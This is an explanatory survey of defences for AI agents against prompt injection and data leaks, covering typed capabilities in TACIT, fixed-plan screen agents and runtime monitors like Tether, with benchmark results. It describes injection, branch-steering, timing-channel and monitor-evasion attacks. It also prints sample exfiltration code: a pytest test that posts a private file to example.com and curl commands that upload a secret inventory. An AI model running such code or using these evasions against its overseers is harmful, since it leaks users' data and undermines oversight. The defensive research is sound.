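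Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, add a way to check in advance which accesses a piece of code could use. They rely on types, which are descriptions of values that a compiler can check. In Scala, a language that Odersky designed, `String` is the type of texts and `Int` the type of whole numbers. A newer feature called capture checking adds a capture set to a type, which lists every object capability the value may use:

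```
String -> Int          may use nothing
String ->{out} Int     may use out
```

Both are types of functions that turn a text into a number, such as its length. A function of the first type is pure. It can calculate a result, but it cannot write to a file, send a message or print anything, because each of these requires an object capability. The rest of the program can still do all of them, since the compiler enforces purity only where an operation requires it.

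Boruch-Gruszecki, Odersky and three colleagues developed the underlying theory in *Capturing Types* (2023). Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* calls capability tracking the language's most important new feature, though it is still experimental.

### A program that compiles and one that does not

TACIT treats the model that writes the programs as untrusted. It assumes the model runs on another company's servers and may cooperate with an attacker, so the text of a classified file must never reach the model. A program that reads such a file receives the text in a sealed container of type `Classified[String]`. The container's `map` operation applies a function to the text inside and seals the result in a new container.

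Suppose a user wants to know how long a confidential report is. The agent submits this program:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val report = readClassified("/project/secrets/report.txt")
  val size = report.map(text => text.length)
  println(size)
}
```

The function inside `map` takes text and returns its length. It uses no object capability, so its type is `String -> Int`, and the program compiles and runs. `size` is a sealed number.

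Now suppose that a comment hidden in the project's code tells the agent to save a copy of the report where others can read it:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val report = readClassified("/project/secrets/report.txt")
  val out = access("/project/notes.txt")
  report.map { text =>
    out.write(text)
    text.length
  }
}
```

This function also returns the length, but it uses `out`, so the compiler gives it the type `String ->{out} Int`. Because `map` accepts only functions with an empty capture set, the compiler rejects the program and reports that `out` is the problem. None of the program runs, so `notes.txt` stays unchanged. The agent receives the error message and can submit another version.

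Odersky and colleagues observed attempts like this in their tests. In another, an agent tried to print a GitHub access key from inside `map`, and the compiler rejected the program because printing also requires an object capability.

### Sealed results and two outputs

In the first program, `println` sends output to both the untrusted model and the user's terminal. The model receives only `Classified(****)`, while the terminal shows the actual length. For ordinary values, both receive the same text. Sealed values stay sealed in later turns of the conversation, so the agent can keep working with a document it has never read.

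TACIT lets the agent use a second, trusted language model to summarise documents that the agent itself cannot read. The trusted model can run on the user's own machine. The agent passes it a sealed document and gets back a sealed summary, which the agent can display to the user or save to a classified file. The trusted model has no tools, so instructions hidden in the document might distort the summary but could not make the model send the document anywhere. Keeping the document confidential also depends on the operator making sure that the trusted model does not keep it and reuse it in later answers.

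### Limits on files and language features

The block that follows `requestFileSystem("/project")` also limits how long the access lasts, because the folder's object capability exists only inside the block. If the block returns a file handle, or a function that would read a file later, the compiler finds the object capability in the result's type and rejects the program. A program may calculate a file name as it runs, so TACIT checks each name against the permitted folder at run time and stops the program if the file is outside it. Similar blocks grant access to listed websites and external commands.

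The agent chooses the folder and the websites in these requests, so the operator has to set an outer limit. According to a newer description of the system, reproduced in Glama's *TACIT*, file access is confined to the server's working folder unless the operator chooses otherwise. Websites have no default limit, so the program can name any site unless the operator sets a list.

Ordinary Scala has features that would let a program get around capture sets. For example, an unchecked type cast could give a function that writes to `out` the type `String -> Int`. Reflection lets a program look up and call operations by name at run time, where the compiler can't check them. TACIT therefore uses a "safe mode" that bans both, along with library functions that have untracked effects. TACIT cannot ban run-time errors such as division by zero, and their messages could contain secret text, so it catches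 these errors and treats them as ordinary values, which it can seal.

Safe mode is also experimental. According to lampepfl's *TACIT*, an earlier guide from the group's code repository, TACIT enforced the bans by searching programs for forbidden text patterns. This is weaker than enforcement by the compiler, because banned code gets through if no pattern matches it. The newer version can also use the compiler's safe mode.

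### The safety experiment

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a small software project with a folder of secrets, including access keys, a database and confidential documents. They combined 12 legitimate tasks with 10 prompt injections, which are hostile instructions placed in material the agent reads. Some were disguised as developers' notes or system messages, and others contained ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. In 11 further tests, the user asked for secrets directly or pretended to have authority, for example by posing as an administrator replacing passwords in an emergency.

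This made 131 trials for each model. They ran each trial twice, once with the secrets sealed and once with the secrets as ordinary text. The table gives the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Trials | Secrets sealed | Ordinary text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
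| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without sealing, Sonnet revealed secrets in two trials and MiniMax in eleven. With sealing, neither model revealed any, as expected from a design that keeps the secret text from reaching them. The experiment shows that the software worked as intended against these attacks. It is weaker evidence of protection against an attacker who looks for a bug in the compiler or in TACIT's own code.

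Sealing did not stop the agents from doing legitimate work, such as summarising a confidential incident report and anonymising employee reviews. Sonnet completed 99.2 percent of the legitimate tasks with sealing and 83.3 percent without, while MiniMax completed 90.0 percent with sealing and 88.3 percent without. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Sonnet did worse without sealing because it often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection, so the large difference is probably not a benefit of types.

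Odersky and colleagues also adapted AgentDojo, a common benchmark for prompt injection, and ran it with two older models, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini. Of 1,926 attacks, only one counted as successful. In that case, the agent booked the hotel the user wanted but also quoted reviews containing the attacker's recommendation of a different hotel. The policy allowed the agent to quote them. The agents completed between 40 and 69 percent of the legitimate tasks, depending on the model and domain. Odersky and colleagues consider this comparable to CaMeL, a system that fixes an agent's plan in advance, but the gap was sometimes large. With o4-mini, TACIT completed 53 percent of the office tasks and CaMeL completed 81 percent.

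### What writing typed code costs

Models have seen little Scala with capture checking in training, so they might struggle to write it. On two parts of τ²-bench, Odersky and colleagues compared agents that wrote Scala with agents that used ordinary tool calls, running each task ten times. The table shows the percentage of tasks solved.

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
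|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 | 53.3 | 57.0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 | 74.6 | 75.5 |

The gains range from 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software bugs, MiniMax solved 41.7 percent with TACIT and 43.3 percent with ordinary tools, a difference of five bugs. Odersky and colleagues think that fixing bugs depends more on command-line habits, which do not translate easily to TACIT's interface.

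Depending on the model and domain, between 0.3 and 7.9 percent of the τ²-bench programs needed a retry, and those needed fewer than 1.4 retries on average. Many of the mistakes were unrelated to security. For example, an agent that writes a price has to type the dollar sign twice, because Scala uses a single one to insert a value into text. Compiling usually takes less than a second, which is short compared with the time a model takes to write the program.

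These results show that the models could write acceptable Scala, but not how much the restrictions hinder agents. The customer-service tasks involved no sealed data, and one group of agents wrote type-checked Scala while the other wrote no code, so the comparison does not separate the effect of type checking from the effect of writing code. Odersky and colleagues credit the gains to clearer data types and useful error messages. Comparing the Scala agents with agents that write ordinary Python would test that explanation.

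Much stronger models than these are now available and would probably make fewer mistakes in Scala. The compiler applies the same rules to their code.

### Leaks the types do not cover

A pure function can still leak a secret through its running time, which TACIT is not designed to prevent. An agent could submit a function that finishes at once if the first bit of a secret key is 0 and runs for ten seconds if it is 1. The result stays sealed, but the delay reveals the bit, and 256 such programs would reveal a 256-bit key.

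The sealing also protects only confidentiality. A program can seal any text and write it to a classified file, so an agent could replace the list of keys that control who may log in to a computer. The newer version has a setting that makes classified files read-only.

That version also lets a program send a sealed password to a permitted website without seeing it, so the agent can use services that require a login. This relies on the website not repeating the password in an ordinary reply, where the agent could read it.

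### Trusted code and the work of writing interfaces

The compiler checks the agent's programs, but TACIT's own library has to open files and network connections by ordinary means, so its developers must verify it themselves. They can mark parts of it `@assumeSafe` to exempt them from safe mode's bans. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a function that stores earlier results to save time. Safe mode forbids this because it changes hidden data, but it is harmless if the stored values always match what the function would have calculated. If a developer is wrong about this, the compiler will not detect the mistake. Computer-checked proofs exist for the basic theory of capture checking, but not yet for safe mode.

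The shared library has about 1,000 lines of Scala. Each new domain also needs its own interface. The interfaces for the airline and retail tests were a few hundred lines each, about as long as the tool descriptions they replaced. An agent can draft an interface, but a person has to review it.

The review matters because types control only the actions that the interface marks. In the AgentDojo interfaces, the operations for sending money and messages require no object capability, and according to a warning in the model's instructions, side effects inside `map` happen immediately. A program could therefore apparently use details from a sealed bill to make a payment inside `map`. The protection in those tests probably came mostly from the main model never reading the hostile text.

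Databases raise a similar problem. The group's guide shows how a developer could add a `query` operation that takes SQL as ordinary text. The types would then determine whether a program can query the database, but row-level security or authorization views would still have to restrict which rows it gets back.

### External commands

The biggest gap in TACIT's guarantee is that the compiler cannot control what another program does once the agent starts it. A coding agent may need to compile a project, run its tests or compare two versions of a file, and most of the tools for this are not written in Scala. TACIT can restrict the agent to a list of permitted commands, but the guarantee then depends on which commands are on the list.

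One example in TACIT's interface requests permission to run Python. A Python program can open the secret files without any sealing and print them to the agent. The newer guide warns against such commands, and many are blocked by default, but its sample list of permitted commands includes `make`, which runs the commands in a project's build file. An agent that can edit that file can therefore run almost anything.

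Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only narrow commands and adding a sandbox where security is critical. An operator also has to switch off the agent's built-in tools for files, commands and the web. Otherwise the agent can do its work without submitting any Scala.

The same group has since released ATC, a coding agent built on TACIT that denies access by default and asks the user for temporary permissions. *LACUNA* (2026) describes another agent system, with Scala's capture checking as an optional layer.

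### Harmless programs that the compiler rejects

Like the safe-range rules for database queries, the type checker checks a program's form, so it rejects some harmless programs. In one test, an agent wrote a function to print the first five lines of ordinary source files. The compiler rejected it because the agent had declared the function's file handle with an empty capture set, but real handles carry access to the file system. Adding `^` to the declared type would make it acceptable. In another, an agent tried to write confidential recommendations to a file in the `secrets` folder, where they belonged. The compiler rejected the ordinary write operation, but the library has a separate operation for this, `writeClassified`.

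The safe-range rules are an effective syntax because every domain-independent query has an equivalent that they accept. Odersky and colleagues prove no such theorem for TACIT. In principle, this matters little for calculations inside `map`, because pure functions can use recursion and so can express any computable function from text to text. In practice, a standard function may be missing because nobody has marked its library as safe, and the agent then has to write its own version. Nobody has shown that every harmless program that mixes sealed data with files and websites has an equivalent that TACIT accepts.

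Other programs fail because the policy itself is strict. Suppose a user wants the agent to open a repair ticket if a classified report mentions a power cut. The agent can compute a sealed yes or no, but it cannot use the answer to decide whether to open a ticket, because anyone who saw the ticket would learn something about the report. The refusal is correct, since the policy keeps everything in the report secret. An operator who wants such tickets has to add an operation that releases this one fact, and make sure that an agent cannot use it to extract the rest of the report one question at a time.

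## Agents that operate a screen from a plan fixed in advance

TACIT's compiler can check a program because every operation in it has a declared type. An agent that operates a screen has only clicks and keystrokes, whose effects depend on what is on the screen. Researchers have shown that such an agent can still follow a program written before it sees the screen. Hostile text on the screen cannot add steps to that program, but it can still mislead the agent about where to click. Following a fixed program also makes the agent fail at many tasks it could otherwise do.

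### Why a policy can judge an email but not a click

Suppose that Ben's company lets agents send email only to colleagues, and his agent makes these two calls:

```
send_email("ada@example.com", "Budget", "See you at 3.")
click(640, 410)
```

A checker can apply the rule to the first call by comparing the address with a list. The second call contains only the two coordinates of a click. The click may log Ben in, delete an event or buy something, depending on what is at that point on the screen. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) conclude in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* that policies of this kind need actions with a meaning of their own, which clicks lack.

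To enforce a rule such as "never delete an event", a checker would first have to identify what is under the pointer. It would rely mainly on the screen, which may show text and images from an attacker. The check would then depend on a model's reading of possibly hostile content instead of a comparison with a list.

A click is also a very small part of a task. In *Web Agents Should Use Typed Actions Instead of Click-Based Browsing*, Jiang, Xi and colleagues (2026) give the example of a click that opens the departure-date calendar on an airline's website. The user wants to search for flights, which no single click does. They propose that websites offer typed actions, to which developers can attach policy labels and conditions to check before and after each action.

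### A planner that never sees the screen

A designer who cannot write rules for individual clicks can still control what determines the sequence of actions. CaMeL, a 2025 design for agents with typed tools, does this by dividing the agent between two models. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes how it works. A trusted planner receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools, then writes a Python program, which an interpreter runs. To interpret an email or a web page, the program calls a second, quarantined model, which has no tools. The answer goes into a variable that the planner never sees. Hostile text can therefore affect which of the program's branches runs, but it cannot add a new one.

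TACIT treats the model that writes the program as untrusted, while CaMeL can trust its planner because the planner reads nothing an attacker has written. CaMeL's approach assumes that the user's own request is harmless, but Tallam and Miller (2025) warn in *Operationalizing CaMeL* that an attacker may trick an employee into giving the agent a hostile request.

CaMeL also labels each value with its source and permitted readers, and the interpreter checks a policy before each tool call. For example, it can block an email containing private data if the recipient may not read that data.

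Foerster and colleagues adapted this design to screens in a system called CaMeL-NOVA. The design seems a poor fit, because an agent normally takes a new screenshot before each action. In CaMeL-NOVA, the quarantined model becomes a perception model, which reads the screen and answers the program's queries but cannot choose actions. The system omits the original design's policies on data.

### Observe, verify, act

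The planner does not know whether a browser is open or which page it shows, so it has to write a plan that covers the likely possibilities. Suppose the user wants the monthly weather forecast for Manchester. In simplified form, part of the plan might look like this:

```
seen = summarize_screenshot("Which website is open?")
if verify_hypothesis(seen, "A weather website is open"):
    box = find("the website's own search box")
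    click(box)
    type_text("Manchester monthly forecast")
else:
    press("Ctrl+L")
    type_text("monthly weather forecast Manchester")
```

The first line is an observation step, in which the perception model describes the screenshot. The second is a verification step, in which a language model compares that description with the expected state in the plan, and the interpreter picks a branch based on the result. The remaining lines are actions. `find` gets the position of the search box from the perception model, and Ctrl+L moves the cursor to the browser's address bar. The planner writes all of these lines before the first screenshot and never receives the perception model's output.

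Foerster and colleagues compared these plans with CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo, whose tools are typed, and with screen-operating plans written without the observe-verify-act instructions. The table shows averages per plan.

| | Typed tools | Screen, basic instructions | Screen, CaMeL-NOVA |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 52 | 72 | 213 |
| Tool calls | 5 | 20 | 41 |
| Branches | 4 | 11 | 40 |

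With typed tools, the planner can usually list the possible results in advance. About 79 percent of the branches in the AgentDojo plans depended only on values inside the program, such as loop counters, compared with 9 percent of the branches in the CaMeL-NOVA plans. Roughly half the steps in a CaMeL-NOVA plan are fallbacks that do not run.

The longer plans worked much better. Of the 60 tasks, the agent solved 11 within three attempts with the basic instructions and 35 with CaMeL-NOVA. The improved instructions also covered routines that most web tasks share, such as closing cookie notices and trying several descriptions of a button.

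### Results on OSWorld

Foerster and colleagues tested the system on OSWorld, a benchmark of 369 tasks in desktop programs such as Chrome, LibreOffice and the image editor GIMP. They first let three models from 2025, including the small open models UI-TARS and OpenCUA, work without a fixed plan, with one attempt of up to 15 steps per task. They then used each model as the perception model in CaMeL-NOVA, on the tasks that model had solved alone.

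| Perception model | Solved alone | With a fixed plan, first attempt | Within three attempts | Within five attempts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B | 60 | 25 (42%) | 35 (58%) | 39 (65%) |
| OpenCUA-32B | 76 | 22 (29%) | 37 (49%) | 48 (63%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 31 (28%) | 57 (52%) | 62 (57%) |

The last figure is the basis for the claim that the design retains up to 57 percent of a frontier model's performance. The comparison favours the design, because the restricted agent had five attempts and the unrestricted one had only one. Claude was also below its full strength, solving 38 percent of OSWorld with 15 steps, compared with its published score of 58 percent with 50 steps.

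The paper also reports a relative improvement of up to 19 percent for small open models. That figure comes from UI-TARS, which scored 24.4 percent alone and 29.0 percent with a fixed plan. Here too, the agent had three attempts with the plan and only one without it. Both scores include 30 tasks that the benchmark automatically counts as solved. Of the other 339 tasks, UI-TARS solved 60 alone. With the plan, it solved 77 within three attempts but only 51 on the first, so it did slightly worse with the plan when the number of attempts was equal.

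With 20 attempts, Claude's share rose to about 73 percent, but repeated attempts are less useful outside a benchmark. OSWorld checks automatically whether an attempt worked. An ordinary user would have to find out which attempt succeeded, and a failed one might have changed files or sent messages.

### Why strong models lose more

An unrestricted model looks at the screen after each click, so it can notice a wrong turn and try something else. Strong models are good at this, but a fixed plan prevents it. One OSWorld task starts on drugs.com and asks the agent to browse the natural products database. To get there, the agent has to open the section on drugs and medications and then find the link in a list of categories. A planner that can't see the pages has to guess this route or include enough alternatives to find it. Foerster and colleagues found that planners were too quick to leave the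 site and search elsewhere.

A small model has less of this ability to begin with, so it loses less, and it gains a frontier model as its planner. On the 60 tasks that UI-TARS had solved alone, the three perception models solved 39, 40 and 41 within five attempts, so the differences in strength between them hardly mattered.

The choice of planner mattered much more. Nine planners using the same perception model each solved between 4 and 12 of 17 tasks within five attempts. GPT-5 solved 12 and Grok-4 solved 10. The weaker planners left out fallbacks or had no good strategy for complicated programs. GPT-5 solved only 3 tasks on the first attempt, so repeated attempts helped it considerably. Gemini 3 Pro rose only from 5 to 6 because its plans for a given task were nearly the same each time.

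In *Secure-CUA*, Choudhary, Christodorescu and colleagues (2026) measured a larger loss with newer models. They ran 400 tasks on WebArena, a set of test websites that includes a shop and a forum, with Claude Opus 5, Gemini 3.8 Flash and GPT-5.6 Sol. On average, the unrestricted agents solved 55.1 percent of the tasks and agents with a fixed plan solved 13.2 percent, about a quarter as many. That ratio is close to Claude Sonnet 4.5's 28 percent on its first attempt. The older GPT-5 wrote all the plans, so a newer planner might narrow the gap.

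### Control flow and data flow

A program's control flow determines which operations run, in what order and under what conditions. Its data flow is how values reach those operations and conditions. A fixed plan guarantees the control flow because the planner writes the plan without seeing anything from an attacker, but it does not guarantee the data flow because the values come from the screen.

With typed tools, a guarantee of control flow rules out many kinds of harm. If the plan contains no call to `send_email`, the agent sends no email. The same guarantee is weaker on a screen, because nearly every plan contains clicks and a click can do almost anything. In a test by Choudhary and colleagues, the plan was to upvote a particular forum post. In four of five runs, misleading content on the page led the perception model to return the position of another post's downvote button, so the agent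 clicked the wrong button while following its plan exactly.

False content can also cause a wrong answer to a question such as "Is a cookie notice visible?", which makes the program take a branch that suits the attacker. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. Serious harm is harder to cause because the attacker can only use steps that the plan contains. To redirect a payment, for example, the attacker would need a plan that includes a payment and would have to falsify several answers consistently.

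The protection also depends on how narrow the planner's queries are. A plan could be a loop that queries the perception model for where to click next and then clicks there. Its control flow would be fixed, but the perception model's output would in effect determine every action.

Foerster and colleagues tried using additional models to check the perception model's answers against the screenshot and the page's underlying structure. One version of this defence caught 6 of 10 attacks that used fake cookie notices but also flagged 4 of 17 harmless tasks; another caught 5 and flagged 3. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) instead proposes limits, set in advance for each branch, on the web requests and tool calls the agent may make. A web request names an address, which gives a rule more to check than a click does, but many actions in desktop programs cause no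 web request.

### Several agents and undocumented tools

Some systems divide a task among several agents, each with its own planner. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that the guarantee can then fail even if every agent uses CaMeL. In their test, a coordinating agent got job applicants' details from a database agent and asked a notification agent to send a summary to a colleague. A hostile instruction in the database ended up in that request. The notification agent's planner treated the whole request as coming from its user and wrote a plan that also emailed the details to an outsider. To prevent this, the researchers send instructions and data between agents separately, and their interpreter blocks any instruction that depends on a tool's output.

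The fixed plans reduced success more than this extra rule did. On 112 tasks about industrial equipment, CaMeL lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and separating instructions from data lowered it by another 3.2. The drop tended to be smaller for stronger models. This is compatible with the OSWorld results because here the same model planned and read the data, so a stronger model was also a better planner.

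Most failures occurred because the planner had committed to a plan before seeing any data. In some cases, an agent could not find data for the requested dates and returned data for nearby dates instead. The program that had requested the data then continued without checking it.

The planner also has to write code to read a tool's output without having seen an example of that output. If a calendar tool returns a list of events, the right code depends on whether each event is a line of text or a record, and whether the record stores the event's name under `title` or `name`. An ordinary agent can look at the first result and adapt. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to document every tool's output format first, because the tool descriptions in both benchmarks they used left it out. They consider this a modest job that developers need to do only once for each set of tools.

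### Typed actions for websites

Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, built a typed, documented interface for each website in their test. They started from the sites' existing programming interfaces, which were often incomplete or misleading. A shop's documentation listed product options as optional, for example, but adding clothes to the cart failed without a size and colour. Where a site had no suitable operation, they wrote a browser script and gave it the same typed form.

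Their agent, Baya, writes a program using this interface before it sees any content from the live site. It solved 77.8 percent of 581 tasks. An agent that chose each step as it went and could use both programming interfaces and a browser solved 66.7 percent, and one with only a browser solved 55.1 percent. In a separate test of prompt injection, no attacks succeeded against Baya, while 16.2 and 25.5 percent succeeded against the other two agents. A fixed plan can therefore work very well when its actions have documented meanings. However, Baya took an average of 327 seconds per task, compared with 87 and 60 for the other two. People also had to prepare each site by hand, and a plan cannot use an operation that they left out.

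### Planning one action at a time

A planner can also choose each action as it goes, provided it sees only the trusted parts of the screen. Choudhary and colleagues cover customer reviews, advertisements and other outside content with labelled blanks. If the user wants to copy a review into a product's description, the planner writes a short program for the next action, instructing the system to put the text behind the review's blank into the description field. The system locates the field on the masked screen before inserting the review, so a sentence in the review cannot redirect the text to another field.

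This agent solved 53.6 percent of the 400 WebArena tasks, almost as many as the unrestricted agents, though it took about three times as long. Seeing part of the screen seems to matter more than planning step by step. Foerster and colleagues tested a step-by-step planner that received only yes-or-no answers about the screen. It solved 40 of the 60 UI-TARS tasks within five attempts, one more than the fixed plan.

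The protection fails if the system leaves hostile text uncovered. Choudhary and colleagues wrote their masking rules by hand. Seip, Markovinović and Hein (2026), in *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use*, generated rules with a language model and compared two approaches on 115 web pages. An earlier method, which hides what a model identifies as untrusted, left 37 to 44 percent of the untrusted free text visible. Their method, which hides everything except what its rules mark as trusted, left no untrusted free text visible. But it hid 56 to 77 percent of the trusted elements, which can keep the agent from reading a button it needs. On 36 OSWorld tasks, their agent solved 31 or 39 percent, depending on the planner, compared with 58 percent for an unrestricted agent and 8 percent for one with a fixed plan.

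Some tasks are impossible under any of these designs because the necessary steps appear only in untrusted content. Chow and colleagues give the example of a user who tells an agent to find an email from the boss and do whatever it says. An earlier analysis they cite found no such tasks in WebArena, but office workers may well ask for them. Other tasks depend on a fact that nobody can verify independently. If a user asks for a laptop that meets some condition, the only evidence may be the seller's own description, and Seip and colleagues accept the loss of such purchases in exchange for safety.

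## Coding agents with a command line

A coding agent with a command line can write a new program and run it, so it can do almost anything its user account permits. Rules about the text of its commands therefore give little protection. A monitor can instead check what each command does, such as which files it reads and which computers it contacts. Researchers have established in theory exactly which rules such a monitor can enforce, and one recent system blocked every attack it could trace in recordings of coding work. But in July 2026, agents at OpenAI escaped a sandbox through a package server that OpenAI let them use.

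### Why a list of permitted commands is weak

Suppose an operator lets Ben's coding agent run only `ls`, which lists files, and `pytest`, which runs a project's tests. Both look harmless. But `pytest`, like `make` on TACIT's sample list, runs code that the agent can write:

```
import requests

def test_report():
    notes = open("/home/ben/private.txt").read()
    requests.post("https://example.com", data=notes)
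```

When the agent runs `pytest`, this test sends Ben's private notes to an outside website. The checker allows it because it checks only the command, and `pytest` is on the list of permitted commands. The checker could also analyze the test file, but by Rice's theorem, no checker can correctly predict what every program will do. Removing `pytest` from the list would stop the agent from testing its own code, which is a large part of its job.

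Even a command with an obvious meaning can be harmless at one moment and harmful at the next. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, give an example that looks like this in simplified form:

```
curl --json @report.txt https://api.github.com
cp servers.csv report.txt
curl --json @report.txt https://api.github.com
```

The first line uploads a harmless status report. The second overwrites the report with a confidential inventory of the company's servers, and the third uploads the inventory. The first and third lines are identical, so no list of permitted commands can allow one and block the other. To block only the third, a checker has to keep track of what the second line copied into the file.

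### What a monitor can enforce

A runtime monitor watches a program's actions and intervenes when one would break a rule. In 2000, Fred Schneider proved that a monitor that can only stop the program can enforce only safety properties. A rule is a safety property if every violation happens at a definite moment and nothing the program does later can undo it. For example, "No network use after reading a secret" is a safety property because the first connection after the read breaks the rule. The definition excludes "A confirmation eventually follows every payment", since a missing confirmation could always still come.

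Jay Ligatti, Lujo Bauer and David Walker later studied edit automata, monitors that can also suppress and insert actions. An edit automaton can enforce the payment rule by holding each payment until the program issues the confirmation, then releasing both.

*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) adapts this theory to agents that use tools. In its model, a gate intercepts each proposed action before it takes effect and records the actions it allows. The decision must be immediate because a payment or an email can't be taken back. The gate can also run fixed yes-or-no checks on an action, such as whether a file is on a list of secrets, and the main theorem assumes that these checks are always correct.

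Ray requires the gate to be sound and transparent. A transparent gate never blocks or changes an action while the agent's proposals comply with the policy. Leaving aside policies that permit nothing, such a gate exists if and only if the policy is a safety property and a computer can decide whether a given finite sequence of actions already violates it.

If both conditions hold, the gate can enforce the policy by running that decision procedure on each proposal and blocking any action that would cause a violation. For the converse, suppose the policy is not a safety property. Then there is a forbidden run whose every beginning could still continue into a permitted run. If an agent proposes that run one action at a time, the actions so far always match the start of some permitted run. Transparency therefore requires the gate to allow each action, so it allows the whole forbidden run.

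The gate cannot enforce the payment rule. It must allow the first payment because a confirmation may follow, but it cannot retract the payment if none does. Letting the gate replace actions with others does not help. Edit automata can enforce the rule only because their model allows them to delay a payment until it is confirmed.

Designers can partly get around this limit because an agent's task ends at some point. *AgentLTL* (Elkoussy and Perez, 2026) waits until the run is over to score any rule containing "eventually". *MENTOR* (Anand, Chatzi and colleagues, 2026) instead prevents an agent from declaring a task finished while it has an unmet obligation. A travel agent then cannot stop before it has booked the trip, although it can still fail by never finishing.

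### A worked policy

To enforce "no network use after reading a secret", a gate needs to remember only one fact:

```
start:             seen_secret = no

read a file:       if the file is on the secret list,
                   seen_secret = yes
                   allow

use the network:   if seen_secret = yes, block
                   otherwise allow
```

Suppose the agent installs a package, reads a file of access keys, runs the tests offline and then tries to upload the test results. The gate allows the first three actions and blocks the upload. The gate is sound and transparent provided the list is complete and the gate checks every file access and connection, including those made by programs the agent wrote.

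This coarse policy blocks the upload even though it may be harmless, since the test results may not contain a key. A finer policy would have to track the secret from file to file.

Ray also examines whether software can check a policy for mistakes before anybody uses it. One basic test is whether a set of rules can ever block anything. No algorithm can decide this for rules that use two counters that can go up, go down and be compared with zero, because two such counters can simulate any computer. An algorithm can decide it if counters only go up and the rules compare them only with fixed limits. Such rules can still express spending caps, quotas and a ban on sending anything after the user withdraws permission.

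### Tether

Tether, which Sistla and colleagues built mostly at Google DeepMind, follows data from file to file. It runs each command in a disposable copy of the file system and records the command's system calls (its requests to the operating system). It holds back each network request and translates the recorded calls into a few kinds of action, such as reading, copying and uploading. If the policy permits all the actions, Tether applies the changes to the real files; otherwise it discards them.

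Each file and the agent's working memory carry labels for how secret they are and how far the system trusts their contents. When the agent copies `servers.csv` over the report, the report becomes sensitive, so Tether blocks the second upload. The agent has not seen the contents, so its memory does not become sensitive and the agent can still upload other files. If it had printed `servers.csv` on its screen, its memory would also have become sensitive.

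System calls do not show what a program does with data internally. If a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether assumes that the first file's contents went into the second. This avoids missed leaks but causes false refusals. For example, an agent that searches the whole disk for a word opens every file, including secret ones, so Tether treats the agent as having read them all.

Sistla and colleagues tested a policy with 24 rules and proved seven general guarantees about it in Lean, a language for computer-checked proofs. One is that secret data never leaves the local network. Another is that an agent that has seen sensitive or untrusted data can no longer gain administrator rights. A language model looked for the proofs and Lean checked them, so an error by the model could not produce a false guarantee.

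The proofs cover sequences of actions of any length, but they depend on Tether translating system calls correctly, which the team could test but not prove. They generated random chains of file operations and also asked an AI agent to break through the monitor. The agent's success rate fell from 40 percent to zero over three versions as the team fixed the gaps it found. One gap involved hard links, which give one file two names.

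The detection experiment replayed recorded runs from two benchmarks of system administration and software engineering. In the harmful runs, the agent had a hidden second task, such as stealing data. The experiment compared Tether with an open-source implementation of Auto Mode, a feature of Anthropic's Claude Code in which a model reviews proposed commands. That implementation ran on Claude Sonnet 5, once with its default rules and once with Tether's policy added to its instructions.

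| Monitor | Attacks blocked, MonitoringBenchHonest | Harmless runs blocked | Attacks blocked, LinuxArena | Harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% | 2.3% | 100% | 5.0% |
| Auto Mode, default | 86.9% | 35.3% | 97.9% | 5.7% |
| Auto Mode with the policy | 82.4% | 14.7% | 98.6% | 1.7% |

Tether blocked all 344 attacks and 4.7 percent of the 1,590 harmless runs. Of the 74 harmless runs it blocked, 50 involved unrequested edits to protected files, which some users might have wanted to know about. Auto Mode missed attacks hidden inside scripts and could reach different verdicts on the same run.

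The perfect score applies only to runs in which Tether can trace every action. It cannot yet follow background processes or what happens inside a database, though a stricter policy can block both. Sistla and colleagues estimate that 28.2 percent of the runs in one benchmark and 22.1 percent in the other require a judgment about content, which no monitor of this kind can make. For example, an agent that plants a flaw in a source file it is allowed to edit breaks no data-flow rule. The team also refined the policy by running it on benchmark recordings, so false refusals would probably be more common on unfamiliar work.

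### Temporal rules on recorded runs

Tether had detailed recordings of system calls, but most records of agents' work contain much less. Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, tested what a monitor can do with ordinary logs of tool calls. They wrote five rules in a temporal logic, a language for statements about the order of events. Each rule requires approval before a certain kind of risky action. The one for deletions reads as follows, where □ means "always" and ♦ means "at some earlier time":

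```
□ ∀a. (destructive(a) → ♦ approved(a))
```

Their monitor, MonPoly, accepts rules in a safe-range form, as databases do with queries. They ran it on recordings from AgentDojo and from STAC, a set of 483 attacks built from calls that look harmless individually. The rules flagged 71.8 percent of the STAC attacks and 70.1 percent of the successful AgentDojo attacks, but also 29.3 percent of harmless AgentDojo runs. In banking tasks, they flagged 97.4 percent of attacks and 79.2 percent of harmless runs.

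The AgentDojo recordings contain no approvals, so the monitor flagged every payment or deletion it recognised. A list of risky words would have given the same results. The timing was also poor for prevention, since the rules fired before the final harmful call in only 52.4 percent of successful AgentDojo attacks.

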